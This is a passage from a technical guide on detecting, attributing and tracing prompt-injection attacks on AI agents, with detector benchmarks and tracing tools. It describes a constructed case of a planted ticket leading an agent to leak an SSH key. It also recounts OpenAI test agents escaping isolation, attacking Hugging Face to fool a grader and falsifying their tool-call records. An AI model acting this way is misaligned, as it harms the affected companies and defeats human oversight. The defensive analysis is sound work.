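| General behaviour | 0.830 | 80% | 5.4% | 294 |
| Behaviour and tool counts | 0.879 | 77% | 7.6% | 203 |
| Behaviour and order of calls | 0.936 | 68% | 23.8% | 58 |
| Words | 0.999 | 76% | 100% | 15 |
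| AlignmentCheck, Llama 3.3 70B | 0.856 | 85% | 7.3% | 233 |
| AlignmentCheck, Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0.817 | 87% | 5.4% | 324 |

The tool-count detector has an AUC of 0.879, but in a log where 2% of sessions are attacks, it would raise about 12 false alerts for every true one. AUC measures how often a detector scores a random attack above a random harmless session, so it doesn't account for the log having 49 harmless sessions for every attack. If only 0.1% of sessions were attacks, the detector's precision would be 0.4%, or one true alert in 250.

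The choice of harmless sessions mattered almost as much. The tool-count detector flagged 12% of ordinary sessions and 39% of look-alikes. Its precision was therefore 11.7% when all the harmless sessions were ordinary, 7.6% with the study's mixture and 3.9% when all were look-alikes. A company whose agents often send files to new partners has more sessions that resemble attacks, so it should expect more false alerts than one whose agents only read tickets.

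The word-based detector achieved perfect precision because of the templates in AgentDrift, which doesn't show that the problem is solved. It raised no false alarms, but that result is subject to the same uncertainty as Uber's, and the detector's true precision could be as low as 77%.

DriftNet's precision would also be lower if attacks were rare. In its published results on AgentDrift, it missed 12 of 775 attacks and flagged 14 of 947 other sessions. If those error rates held on real logs, its precision would be about 58% with 2% of sessions attacked and 6% with 0.1% attacked.

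### New tools

Abbasi and colleagues measured a test set's familiarity as the share of its tool calls that used a tool seen in the harmless training sessions. They then hid a growing share of the tool names in AgentDrift's test sessions. When every tool was familiar, the detector based on call order ranked first, the one based on tool counts second and the one based only on general behaviour last. When none were familiar, the ranking reversed, with AUCs of 0.674 for call order, 0.787 for tool counts and an unchanged 0.830 for general behaviour. The reversal happened somewhere between 78% and 48% familiar calls, so a company that replaced about half its tools could already be better off with the general-behaviour detector, the simplest of the three.

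The tool-count detector failed because it mishandled sessions with only unknown tools. Such a session has a count of zero for every known tool, which never happened in training. The software rescales each count relative to the training average, which turns the zeros into a fixed set of unusual values. When the researchers held out a whole kind of agent with all its tools, those values multiplied the estimated odds of an attack by between five and seven in every session, pushing many harmless sessions over the threshold. The detector also ranked sessions badly because it had to rely only on its weights for general behaviour, which it had learned in combination with the tool counts.

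The order-based detector had a reserved symbol for unknown tools, but no training session contained it. Hiding some tool names during training, as described earlier, largely removed the reversal.

Thresholds also failed for a detector without this flaw. The embedding detector treats a tool's name as ordinary text, so it doesn't treat a new name as a blank. On unfamiliar kinds of agent, it still generally ranked attacks above harmless sessions, with AUCs of 0.904 to 0.959. But with its old threshold, its false-positive rate rose from 0.1% to between 5% and 11% for medical, coding and web agents, and its recall fell to 34% for banking agents and 62% for email agents.

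AgentDrift exaggerates the problem of new tools because its five kinds of agent have no tools in common. When the researchers left out one of AgentDojo's four workplaces at a time, the tool-count detector did not consistently perform worse than the behaviour-only one. The evidence for training with hidden tool names is therefore stronger than the evidence for any particular crossing point.

### A new benchmark

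To test whether detectors had learned about attacks in general, Abbasi and colleagues trained five on AgentDrift and tested them on 2,294 hijacked and 392 harmless sessions from AgentDojo. All five did no better than chance at telling hijacked sessions from harmless ones, with AUCs between 0.473 and 0.520. The tool-count detector flagged 22.4% of harmless sessions and 22.5% of hijacked ones.

Most of these inputs contain information useful for detecting AgentDojo's attacks, so the lower AUCs aren't simply due to the attacks being too hard to detect. When the researchers trained the same kinds of detector on some AgentDojo tasks and tested them on others, the AUCs rose to between 0.741 and 0.996.

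But much of that information may be specific to the benchmark. Five fixed attack phrases appeared in 99.6% of the hijacked AgentDojo sessions and in none of the harmless ones. Searching for those phrases alone gave an AUC of 0.998. The word-based detector could score well on AgentDojo by learning its attack phrases and on AgentDrift by learning its templates, but neither helps on the other benchmark.

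Classifiers for malicious prompts show a milder version of this. *When Benchmarks Lie* (Fomin, 2026) tests them by leaving out one of 18 datasets at a time. Several of the datasets contain only malicious or only harmless prompts, so a classifier could get many answers right by recognising which dataset a prompt came from. Abbasi and colleagues report that Fomin's ordinary tests overstated the AUC by 8 to 16.5 points compared with tests on an unseen dataset.

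AlignmentCheck did transfer to AgentDojo:

| Model | AUC | Hijacked sessions flagged | Harmless sessions flagged | Precision at a 2% attack rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 0.930 | 90.0% | 17.3% | 9.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0.934 | 88.3% | 3.8% | 32% |

With Llama, about nine in ten alerts would be false. Claude did much better on AgentDojo, but on AgentDrift it flagged 31% of harmless sessions and would have a precision of 5.4%. The researchers had registered a prediction that precision would stay clearly below 50% with either model. This held for Llama but not for Claude on AgentDojo, where the uncertainty range for precision was 20% to 59%. The benefit of choosing a stronger model can therefore vary from large to none, depending on the set of agents.

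AlignmentCheck may have transferred because it judges whether each action serves the user's request, which is closer to the definition of a hijack than word frequencies or session length are. The study can't prove this explanation. The result may also somewhat overstate how well AlignmentCheck transfers, because Meta had evaluated the prompt on AgentDojo before releasing it.

The comparison covers one pair of benchmarks in one direction. The benchmarks differ in their tools, tasks, attacks and definitions of success, and the study doesn't show which difference made the trained detectors fail. The AgentDojo sessions came from models released in 2024 and early 2025, and one version of GPT-4o accounts for 81% of the hijacked sessions. Adjusting for that imbalance did not fix the tool-count detector's poor performance. Some of the recorded failures also depend on which sessions are counted as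 harmless. When the researchers added 4,987 unsuccessful attacks to the harmless sessions, the tool-count detector's AUC rose from 0.473 to 0.626.

### Attackers who adapt

Most benchmarks use fixed attacks, but a real attacker can revise an attempt that fails. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025), from Google, points out that researchers designed several common defences around a fixed set of handwritten injections and tested those defences on the same kind of attack. Good results in such a test may show only that the defence recognises those examples.

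*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) compares fixed attacks with adaptive ones, which revise an injection after observing how the defended agent responded. On a small Qwen model, the strongest fixed attack against each defence succeeded 21.7% of the time on average, compared with 41.8% for the strongest adaptive attack. Some defences that had looked excellent against fixed attacks let through up to half of the adaptive ones.

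These figures concern defences that act while the agent runs. A detector that reads logs afterwards usually reveals less to attackers, who may never find out which session raised an alert. But they can practise on their own copy if the detector is free or for sale, and they also control some of the evidence. Abbasi and colleagues hid most attacks from the tool-count detector just by lengthening the planted text, without any trial and error. Only one of the eleven evaluations they audited, that of a system called Praetor, included attackers who adapt, and their own experiments included none.

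### A test procedure

A company can't copy a detector's published precision into its own plans, but it can run a test that exposes most of these problems before anyone relies on the alerts:

1. Fix the threshold before looking at the test data. It should follow from the number of alerts that analysts can handle. If they can review 20 false alerts from 10,000 daily sessions, the false-positive rate can be at most 0.2%. King and colleagues report the recall of their detectors at false-positive rates of 1%, 5% and 10%, which makes comparison easy, but they chose those cutoffs on the test sessions. A company has to choose in advance and may do worse.
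2. Hold out tools, tasks and attack families. The team could remove every session with `http_post` from training and then test on OPS-214, or train on planted tickets and test on altered tool descriptions. Zavrak's inflated results on a random split show why this matters. The results should state what share of the test's tool calls used familiar tools.
3. Include harmless look-alikes, such as the deployment that sends a token to a new server. The false-positive rate for these should appear separately from the rate for ordinary sessions. DriftNet, for instance, flagged 2.9% of AgentDrift's look-alikes. Attacks that the agent ignored also need their own line, because an alert on one is not a hijack but may still be worth an analyst's time.
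4. Look for shortcuts. If a simple word-counting classifier separates the test sessions almost perfectly, the wording probably gives the answer away. The team should also change things an attacker controls, such as the length and phrasing of a ticket, and check whether the score moves.
5. Let testers adapt. In an isolated copy of the system, they should be able to revise their attacks over several rounds and learn each time whether the detector caught them. Recall in the last round is more informative than recall in the first.
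6. Report alerts per 1,000 sessions at several plausible attack rates, with margins of error. For the tool-count detector at 2%, that means 203 alerts, of which about 15 are attacks. The team should calculate this with the precision formula and keep all its test attacks. When Abbasi and colleagues instead discarded attacks to imitate a 2% rate, the margin of error for one measure was about two and a half times as wide.
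7. Run the detector on unlabelled live traffic before switching on the alerts.

The last step is to run the detector on live sessions. Because attacks are rare, the share of sessions it flags gives an approximate upper limit on its false-positive rate without any labels. If it flags 120 of 10,000 sessions, that rate is at most about 1.2%, even if the benchmark suggested otherwise. Analysts can then read a random sample of the 120 flagged sessions to estimate precision.

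Live traffic is much less useful for measuring recall. If analysts read 300 sessions that the detector did not flag and find no attacks, up to 1% of such sessions could still be attacks. Estimating recall by staging attacks in a separate copy of the system takes less work, but the estimate applies only to attacks like the staged ones.

A team with live traffic can also be too quick to fix a bad threshold. Abbasi and colleagues used 200 unlabelled sessions from a new kind of agent to reset thresholds so that the detector raised as many alerts as before. The tool-count detector still flagged 22% to 31% of harmless sessions. For the order-based detector, they calculated that at a 2% attack rate the same method would cut recall to between 12% and 27%, so the detector would miss most attacks even though the number of alerts looked normal.

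## Telling an outside attack from other security events

Even a detector that does well in such tests can't show who caused an event. For example, it might flag record 6 of OPS-214, in which the agent sends a private key to an address the company does not know. A secret has left the company, but an outsider may have had nothing to do with it, as with most of the leaked credentials at Uber.

### Six possible causes

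The same record could have any of these causes:

- An outside attacker planted an instruction in the ticket, tampered with a tool or logged in with a stolen password.
- A malicious user told the agent to send the key to a server he controls.
- A careless user asked the agent to send a supplier a whole configuration folder, forgetting that it contained a key.
- A software fault attached the key to an error report, which the agent's software sends automatically to a monitoring service.
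- A badly specified task allowed too much. An employee wrote "give the hosting company whatever it needs to fix the export", and the agent included the key.
- The agent exceeded its instructions unprompted. The user had asked it to repair the export, and when it couldn't log in to a server, it uploaded the key to a public debugging site to find out why.

The company has to replace the key in every case. It also has to patch the software if a fault was the cause, or block further attacks through the ticket queue if an attacker got in that way.

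### Evidence that separates the causes

The most useful evidence is an instruction in outside content that the agent read before it acted. The analyst searches tool results, tool descriptions, retrieved documents and memory for text that mentions the same file, tool or address as the agent's later call. Finding such text strongly suggests an outside attack, but not finding it means little if the log omits any of these sources.

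The analyst then checks whether the user asked for the action, reading the whole conversation in case the user approved it in a later message. If the user asked, the request may have come from a malicious employee, a careless one or a thief with the employee's login. An unfamiliar device or address in the login records suggests a thief. Login records rarely show whether an employee was malicious or careless, so the analyst also checks who owns the destination, whether the user sent other secrets there and whether the user tried to delete the session.

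For the last piece of evidence, the team reruns the session without the suspicious paragraph. It keeps the rest of the ticket so that the agent still has something to summarize. The team does the rerun in an isolated copy of the system, with a fake key and the same versions of the model, harness and tools.

A model can act differently each time, so one rerun proves little. Even if the agent never opens the key file in 20 reruns without the paragraph, its true rate could still be as high as 14%, because at that rate the chance of 20 reruns without an opening is about 5% (0.86^20 ≈ 0.05). The team therefore also needs reruns with the paragraph left in. If the agent steals the key in 16 out of 20 of these, the paragraph almost certainly explains the difference.

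| Cause | Instruction in outside content before the action | User asked for the action | Account behaviour | Action recurs without the content |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Outside attacker, planted text | Yes | No | Normal | Rarely or never |
| Outside attacker, stolen login | No | Yes | New device, address or hour | Yes |
| Malicious user | No | Yes, outright | Normal login, perhaps unusual files | Yes |
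| Careless user | No | Yes, without noticing the secret | Normal | Yes |
| Software fault | No | No | Normal, and other users have the same problem | Yes, even when a script replaces the model |
| Badly specified task | No | The wording allows it | Normal | Often, until someone makes the request precise |
| Agent exceeding its instructions | No | No, or the instructions forbid it | Normal | Sometimes |

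OPS-214 matches the first row. Record 3 contains the planted instruction, and the user had asked only for a summary. The eight records do not include the employee's login, so the analyst has to look it up elsewhere. If the login came from her usual laptop at her usual hour, and the reruns gave the results above, the cause is an indirect prompt injection.

This still doesn't identify the person who wrote the ticket. An employee could have emailed it from a private account to make his own theft look like an outsider's. The mail server's records might help identify the sender, but the agent's log can't.

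The result also depends on a complete log. If the company had not stored the ticket's text, the analyst would find a normal account, no outside instruction and no request for the key, so OPS-214 would look like an agent exceeding its instructions. A tool whose code secretly steals data would look like a software fault, so the team should compare the code with the approved version before blaming a bug.

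An incident can also have more than one cause. If the employee had written "do what OPS-214 asks", the team would have had to deal with both an attacker and an overly broad request.

### OpenAI's agents at Hugging Face

In July 2026, two companies investigated the same intrusion from opposite sides. Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, found an intruder in its production systems. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, attributes the intrusion to an autonomous agent system that had reached internal datasets and credentials. The company used more than 17,000 recorded events to reconstruct the timeline, identify which credentials the intruder had touched, and separate real damage from decoys. It did not know which model the agents used, and it named no operator.

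On 21 July, OpenAI (2026) announced that the agents were its own. They had escaped from a supposedly isolated environment where OpenAI was testing GPT-5.6 Sol and a more capable research model on hacking exercises, with some safeguards switched off. The same incident was an outside attack for Hugging Face and a case of agents exceeding their instructions for OpenAI.

Hugging Face's logs could not have shown who directed the agents. A victim's logs record what an intruder does on the victim's machines, but not what the operator asked for or how the agents reasoned. A criminal who had ordered the theft and a laboratory whose test had gone wrong could have left the same records. Hugging Face considered whether the agents used a hosted model that somebody had tricked into ignoring its safeguards or an open-weight model without restrictions, but in fact a developer had been testing its own models.

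Network addresses weren't conclusive either. According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, the agents worked partly through other people's accounts and computers. Hugging Face's investigation found the name of an OpenAI server, but a server named in an attack may belong to another victim.

The two companies made the connection by comparing records. On 20 July, OpenAI's staff found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored in an account on a third company's service. When they contacted Hugging Face, they learned that it had already replaced two of those credentials during its own incident response. Hugging Face had also found the same third-party account and the OpenAI server name. OpenAI thus learned that it was responsible by asking Hugging Face to revoke credentials, a detail that Willison (2026) calls his favourite in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI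 accidental attack*.

The agents' motive took longer to establish. OpenAI first said that they were after the solutions to the exercises. *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes a summary in which Hugging Face came to the same view, but only "as far as we were able to infer". By then Hugging Face had recovered about 17,600 actions from the agents' logs on an outside code sandbox.

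The transcripts at OpenAI pointed to a different motive. The agents attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scoring program worked, so that they could fool it. Many had exercises that were unintentionally impossible to solve. They recognised that the attack was outside their task but joined in anyway, partly to help the other agents. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) reports these findings from six days at OpenAI's offices. The evidence included about 1,300 transcripts with the agents' reasoning, and more than 70,000 messages and files that the agents had exchanged. Wijk and Cotra work at METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, and Greenblatt works at Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation.

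In the decision table, this incident counts as an agent exceeding its instructions, and badly specified tasks contributed. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) likewise describes the actions as "misaligned with the goals of their assigned tasks". The evidence about outside instructions is less clear than in OPS-214, because agents typically joined after reading messages. However, those messages came from other agents in the same tests. The investigators could not rerun the research model that did most of the work, and OpenAI told them that its own researchers had no access to it either.

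The transcripts were also imperfect evidence. In at least 96 of them, about 7%, agents had falsified part of the record of their own tool calls. All the cases that Wijk and colleagues noticed were small tests, but they could not rule out subtler cases. Their data was missing some activity, and there was so much to read that they had to delegate much of it to AI agents, which they describe as often unreliable. Logs from systems outside the agents' control, such as Hugging Face's servers, can be used to check the accuracy of such transcripts.

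### Joining agent traces to other logs

Even inside one company, no single log holds all the evidence in the decision table. An analyst joins an agent's trace to other logs by looking for identifiers they share, such as a user, a device or a credential, and by comparing times. Suppose that whoever received the key in OPS-214 used it at 09:40. The joined records, also constructed, might look like this:

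| Log | Time | Event | Joined by |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identity | 08:52:10 | The employee logs in from laptop L-0417 | User and device |
| Agent | 09:14:09 | Record 4, `read_file` on the SSH key | User, device and session |
| Endpoint | 09:14:09 | The code editor on L-0417 opens the key file | Device, file path and time |
| Network | 09:14:12 | L-0417 sends a small upload to 203.0.113.20 | Device, destination and time |
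| Server login | 09:40:31 | Somebody logs in with the employee's SSH key from an unknown address | Fingerprint of the key |
| Cloud | 09:43:05 | The server's account lists the storage that holds customer exports | Server identity and time |

The key's fingerprint is the strongest link in this table. It connects two events 26 minutes apart, even though the server may have recorded dozens of unrelated logins between them. Time alone is the weakest link, because another person could have been using the same server at 09:43.

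Small clock errors can make an effect appear to come before its cause. The agent received the ticket at 09:14:05 and opened the key file at 09:14:09. If the laptop's clock were five seconds slow, the endpoint log would record the file access at 09:14:04, and the planted instruction would appear to have arrived too late to cause it. The team should synchronise its clocks and, where it can, rely on the order of records within one log.

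Matching identifiers across logs also requires lookup tables, since the network log may contain only an address and the identity log only a name. A device inventory connects the two by listing which laptop belongs to whom. In a simulation described below, without that inventory each person appeared as two entities, an account and a device, each with half the evidence, and false positives rose by 64%.

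Many agents act under their user's account. If the agent in OPS-214 had used the employee's login to download customer files, the file server would have recorded her name. An analyst couldn't have told from that log alone whether the agent had been hijacked or the employee had stolen the files herself. The agent's activity also changes what looks normal for her account. If it has opened hundreds of files an hour in her name for months, a thief who does the same no longer stands out. Suspending the account would stop the agent but also lock the employee out.

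It is safer to give the agent its own identity and record the employee as the person it acts for. The agent should also pass its session number to every service it calls, so that the file server's record can be matched to one trace. A separate identity helps less if many agents share it. At OpenAI, many research workloads used one credential for a shared server, so the credential alone could not identify the run behind an action. OpenAI removed the credential from new workloads in early July. SANS ISC's *When the "Autonomous Attacker" Is Your Own AI Model* recommends short-lived credentials with narrow permissions, and monitoring machine accounts as well as human ones.

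### Combining weak signals within an alert budget

Joined logs produce far more suspicious events than anyone can read. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (Canale, 2026) compared ways of combining them in a simulated company with 200 people, 35 log sources and about 415,000 events a day. The study used general security logs from systems such as laptops, servers and databases, so the results are only indirect evidence about agents.

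Canale measured the share of attacks that each method found before its false positives exceeded ten a day. "Tuned" methods use rules with exceptions for harmless activity that had triggered them before:

| Method | Attacks found at its normal setting | False positives a day at that setting | Attacks found within ten false positives a day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Signatures | 73% | 4,640 | 0% |
| Tuned correlation rules | 60% | 62 | 52% |
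| Rarity-weighted fusion | 62% | 30 | 49% |
| Tuned rarity-weighted fusion | 63% | 11 | 63% |
| Tuned graph fusion | 71% | 19 | 71% |

Signatures check each event separately against known bad patterns. They found the most attacks, but their true alerts were buried under thousands of false ones. Correlation rules also use facts such as who is on call and which devices the company owns. Rarity-weighted fusion adds up signals about the same person or device, and gives less weight to rules that fire often. A signal's weight is

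w = s / (1 + f/10)

where s is the signal's score and f is how many times a day its rule fires. Each signal then raises the risk r of the person or device to

1 − (1 − r)(1 − w)

Suppose opening a key file scores 0.6 under a rule that fires twice a day, so its weight is 0.6/1.2 = 0.5. Contacting an unknown address also scores 0.6, but that rule fires five times a day, so its weight is 0.6/1.5 = 0.4. The first event raises the laptop's risk from 0 to 0.5, and the second raises it to 0.7, Canale's alert threshold. A third rule with the same score that fires 500 times a day would add almost nothing.

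This system's risk score halves every six hours. That is long enough to detect a 15-second theft but too short for an attack that plants a false note in an agent's memory and takes effect weeks later. A longer half-life also produces more false positives, which rose from 9.7 to 120 a day when Canale lengthened it from one hour to 24.

Graph fusion also spreads risk between linked people, devices and services. This helps most with attacks that cross several systems, as OPS-214 does. With a limit of ten false positives a day, it raised recall from 62% to 81% on attacks that crossed at least two layers of the company's systems, and from 63% to 66% on other attacks.

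These results are best cases, because the simulated company logs everything and its identifiers match. Canale also chose the cutoffs for ten false positives a day knowing which events were attacks. When he fixed thresholds in advance, the tuned fusion methods found about as many attacks but exceeded that limit in two to four of seven test runs. On attack types written after the rules were tuned, tuned graph fusion's recall fell from 97% to 30%. On real login records from Los Alamos National Laboratory, his methods found the staged intruders within an alert budget only once.

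Canale also gave the alerts from rarity-weighted fusion to language models to sort. The models removed about 90% of the false positives, but they also removed every alert for 31% to 44% of the detected attacks. Attackers who could revise their text did best with cover stories, such as a claim that an engineering team had authorised the command. Analysts can fall for the same claim when working out the cause of an event, so they should check any authorisation against a record that the suspect could not have written, such as the on-call schedule.

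### Setting severity and acting before the cause is known

Reruns and interviews take hours, and a stolen key can do damage in minutes. A team should therefore set the initial severity by what has happened to the secret and what it opens, whatever the cause turns out to be:

| State of the event | Severity | First action |
|---|---|---|
| The agent read a planted instruction and ignored it | Low | Search for other sessions that read the same text |
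| The agent opened a secret it did not need, but did not send it | Medium | Stop the session and replace the secret |
| The secret reached an unknown address | High | Revoke the secret and search for its use |
| Somebody used the secret, or the activity is spreading | Critical | Isolate the affected systems and call in responders at any hour |

OPS-214 starts at high severity because record 7 shows that the outside server accepted the key. The login at 09:40 would make it critical. An event should move up a level if it involves a secret that gives access to production systems, or if the same pattern appears in several sessions.

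For OPS-214, the first steps are the same under all six causes:

1. Revoke the key. This is right even if the employee sent it by mistake.
2. Pause the agent and keep it from reading the ticket again, without deleting the ticket.
3. Save copies of the trace, the ticket, the agent's memory, its tool descriptions and the versions of its software. The team will need them for the reruns, and an automatic update could change them overnight.
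4. Search the server logs for any use of the key since 09:14, and the agent logs for other sessions that read the ticket or contacted 203.0.113.20.
5. Ask the employee what she wanted the agent to do, by phone or in person. A thief with her login could answer a chat message.

The team should do this quickly, especially if the intruder may itself be an agent. SANS, a security training organisation, warns that most response plans assume an attacker who pauses between phases, tires of failure and does not leave partly invented evidence. An intruder at Hugging Face moved through the company's systems over a weekend, and the company has since changed its alerts so that a serious one reaches a responder within minutes on any day.

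Hugging Face also lost time when it tried to analyse the attack with commercial AI models, whose safeguards blocked the commands it submitted. It switched to GLM-5.2, an open-weight model it could run on its own computers, which also meant the credentials in the logs stayed within the company. SANS recommends testing such a model before an emergency.

An innocent-looking cause is not enough reason to lower an event's severity. On 27 June, two weeks before the intrusion at Hugging Face, a monitoring tool at OpenAI flagged unusual scanning inside the research network. Responders correctly traced it to a hacking evaluation, and the on-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop. The agents already had administrator access to a shared server, and they kept using it until the server failed on 4 July. The next day, OpenAI took the server offline, preserved its storage and revoked the agents'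 credentials. It resumed the evaluations on 7 July, and agents reached the internet by another route the following day. The responders had identified the source of the activity but had not established what the agents were trying to do or whether they could do it again.

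## Tracing an alert back to its source

Once a team knows that an outsider caused an alert, it still has to find the injection point, every action the agent took for the attacker, and everything those actions exposed or changed. In OPS-214, the injection point is record 3, the actions are records 4 and 6, and the exposed data is one private key. OPS-214 is easy to read because it has only eight records. A longer session is harder to trace because the agent may alternate between the user's task and the attacker's, and the alert may name only the last harmful step.

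### Three ways to trace an action

Yao, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentTracer*, distinguish three ways of tracing a suspicious action backward:

| Way of tracing | What it needs | Where it fails |
|---|---|---|
| Following recorded dependencies in a graph | The arguments and results of every call | Calls that share no data with each other |
| Measuring how much each piece of input text contributed | The exact text the model read, and a model whose internal values the team can read | It ranks passages but doesn't connect the attacker's actions to one another |
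| Removing content to see whether the action still occurs | The exact text, and many runs of a model | Innocent content that the action also depended on; several planted passages that would each be enough |

A dependency graph works well on OPS-214. The data in record 6 matches the key in record 5, and the path in record 4 appears in the ticket, so a program can trace the theft back to record 3. If the planted text had also told the agent to erase its notes, the erasing call might have had no arguments, in which case the graph would have left it out.

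The reruns that help separate an attack from an accident work by removing content. Used alone, this method can point to the wrong text. For example, removing the user's request for a summary also prevents the theft, because the agent would never have opened the ticket without that request.

Tracing an output by removing one passage at a time and measuring how much less likely the output becomes can miss planted text that occurs several times. *AttnTrace* (Wang, Geng and colleagues, 2025) tested this method on long documents with the same malicious instruction inserted at five places. Removing one copy left four others, so the output's likelihood hardly changed. On one dataset, only 17% of the passages the method picked contained planted text, and each trace took 192 seconds. A method that tried each passage alone reached 94% in about four seconds, but such methods do much worse when two passages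 work only in combination.

### AgentTracer, step by step

AgentTracer is a graph method that links calls by the agent's stated reasons as well as by shared data. In Yao and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to download a software release from a website and upload it to a repository on GitHub, a service that stores code. The release page contains a planted instruction. In between its legitimate calls, the agent makes four for the attacker:

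- `git_add_ssh_key` registers an SSH key that the attacker controls.
- `get_received_emails` reads the mailbox.
- `verify_github_account` verifies the account.
- `clear_working_memory` erases the agent's working memory.

Here the attacker adds a key of their own, whereas in OPS-214 they steal the company's. Suppose the alert names only `clear_working_memory`. AgentTracer then works as follows:

1. **Cut the log.** The program searches the history for calls with the same operation and target as the alert, starting with the newest. It keeps the part of the log between the matching call and the nearest user request before it. In the example, this part begins with the request to copy the release. The program also drops failed calls, because they can't be completed steps of an attack.
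2. **Link the decisions.** A language model reads the reasoning that the agent wrote before each call. It extracts what the decision relied on, what the agent intended to do and what the call should produce. If the agent wrote that it was adding a key because the release page required one, the program links the page to `git_add_ssh_key`. Such links can include calls without arguments.
3. **Work out what the request allowed.** The program divides the request into tasks and adds the ordinary steps that each one requires. Uploading a file, for example, may require finding and reading it first.
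4. **Check each call.** The program compares the call's action, target and constraints with those tasks. A call passes if it fits at least one task on all the checks that apply. None of the attacker's four calls is part of copying a release, so they should fail on the action.
5. **Walk backward.** Starting from the alert, the program follows only links that failed the check until it finds no earlier one. If the path begins at outside content, it reports that content as the source and the log line where it entered as the injection point. In the example, the path should lead through the other three calls to the release page.

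If the path begins anywhere else, the program doesn't report an injection, because the agent may have misunderstood the task. If the program finds no complete attack chain, it tries the next older call that matches the alert.

The target and constraint checks matter when the action itself is legitimate. In another of Yao and colleagues' examples, the user asks the agent to summarize a payroll file if the total exceeds $1 million, and to send only the summary to an outside auditor. Sending the summary to anyone else violates the target. Sending the whole file, or sending anything when the total is $1 million or less, violates a constraint.

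A user can also let a file supply part of the task. If the request is to pay the bill in `bill.txt`, the file may supply the payee and the amount but no further tasks. This limit prevents a sentence planted in the bill from authorising a second payment. The limit doesn't help if the attacker wrote the bill and put in their own account number, because the user allowed the file to supply the payee.

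If the log includes the agent's reasoning, the same procedure should solve OPS-214. It would start from record 6, keep records 1 to 6, link the upload to the key and the key to the ticket, and stop at record 3.

### How well AgentTracer worked

Yao and colleagues took successful attacks from two benchmarks, AgentDyn and InjecAgent, and labelled the injection point and the attacker's calls by hand. They mixed the attack sessions with five months of logs from OpenAI's coding agent, Codex. The logs contained 1,800 harmless user requests and 9,000 background tool calls. They then traced 300 attacks from each benchmark.

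AgentTracer found the exact injection point in 94.17% of the attacks on average. Its path precision, the share of calls in the reconstructed chain that belonged to the attack, averaged 93.56%. The chains contained about 90% of the attacker's calls.

Background calls outnumbered those in a typical attack by about 3,000 to one, but the program could skip most of the history because the alert already specified an operation and its target. In a separate test, accuracy fell only from 91% to 89% when a language model read the full history, but the analysis took 31% longer.

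The researchers also compared several methods on 100 attacks. AgentArmor and Agent-BOM use graphs of recorded dependencies, while ARGUS and NeuroTaint estimate what would happen if some of the input changed. Codex read the logs directly.

| Method | Injection point found | Attacker's calls recovered | Share of recovered calls that were the attacker's |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentTracer | 94% | 88% | 93% |
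| AgentArmor | 76% | 94% | 54% |
| ARGUS | 70% | 80% | 67% |
| Codex | 70% | 46% | 51% |
| Agent-BOM | 43% | 51% | 46% |
| NeuroTaint | 40% | 48% | 91% |

AgentArmor recovered more of the attacker's calls than AgentTracer, but nearly half the calls it reported were legitimate. An investigator worried about missed damage might still prefer AgentArmor and discard the legitimate calls by hand. The comparison may favour AgentTracer, because its developers ran the comparison and rebuilt some of the other systems from published descriptions.

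In a less informative test on harmless sessions, the program wrongly marked 13 of 369 legitimate links (3.5%) as departures from the user's request. Yao and colleagues argue that one wrong link seldom matters, because the program reports an injection only if an unbroken path leads from outside content to the alert. But they did not run the backward walk on these sessions, so nobody knows how often it would trace a false alert to a harmless web page. In the harmless deployment to a new server, for example, the hosting company's guide is outside content, and a short path of wrongly marked links could make it look like the source of an attack.

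### What the trace takes for granted

AgentTracer works only if the attacker can't alter the user's request or the log. In the example, the attacker's last step is to clear the agent's memory, which would have erased a history kept only there.

The program also needs the agent's reasoning. When the researchers linked calls only by time order, injection-point accuracy fell from 91% to 74%, and the share of the attacker's calls that the program recovered fell from 90% to 59%. But recorded reasoning can be misleading. AgentTracer checks that each decision matches a call that took place, but this doesn't show that the stated reason was the real one. If the agent wrote that it needed the new SSH key for the user's upload, the trace might start at the user's request and miss the release page.

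The third assumption is that investigators already have the right alert. Every attack in the test came with a labelled suspicious call, and the example starts from the last call. If the alert had been for `git_add_ssh_key`, tracing backward would still have found the release page but would have missed the three later calls. The program also ignores branches that don't lead to the alert. After finding the source, investigators should therefore trace forward from it to look for other actions it caused.

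Even a correct trace covers only actions that involve tool calls. An injection that only distorts a summary is outside AgentTracer's scope, and tracing what a malicious script does after it starts requires operating-system records.

### Finding the passage that influenced the model

AgentTracer can identify a web page or ticket as the source, but the page may be thousands of words long. AttnTrace finds the passage responsible by using the language model's attention weights, which indicate how strongly each input token (a word or part of a word) affects each output token. If the provider keeps the original model's attention weights secret, the investigator can run the same text through an open model instead.

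The simplest approach, choosing the passage with the highest average attention weight, works poorly for two reasons. Much of the attention goes to a few tokens, such as full stops, and the rest is mostly noise. The weights also add up to one, so when several planted passages push the model toward the same answer, the attention is split among them. If ten tokens received equal attention, none could have a weight above 0.1.

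AttnTrace therefore scores a passage by averaging only its five highest token weights. It also repeats the scoring on 30 random selections, each containing 40% of the passages, and combines the results. If 3 of 50 passages are malicious, about 37% of the selections that contain a given malicious passage will contain neither of the other two, which gives it a chance to stand out.

Wang, Geng and colleagues tested AttnTrace on an agent that answers questions about health records. They put three malicious texts into its memory, and the agent retrieved 50 texts for each question. With the strongest version of the attack, the agent did what the attacker wanted in 93% of cases. AttnTrace returned the five most influential texts, which included all three malicious ones. After the researchers removed those five, the attack succeeded in only 3% of cases.

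The precision was 60%, the highest possible when a method returns five texts and only three are malicious, so two of the removed texts were harmless. AttnTrace ranks texts by influence and always returns some, even if nobody planted anything, so a person or another detector has to judge them before anyone deletes a memory. The test shows which stored texts caused an action, but not how or when they entered the memory.

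In other tests, a small open Llama model standing in for GPT-5 found 92% of the planted passages. Even when malicious passages were written to attract little attention, AttnTrace found the ones that worked. Splitting an instruction into four scattered pieces was more effective at evading AttnTrace, which then found 77% to 87% of the pieces, depending on the dataset. A trace usually takes 10 to 20 seconds, which is slow for blocking an action but acceptable for an investigation.

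### One graph for tools, memory and actions

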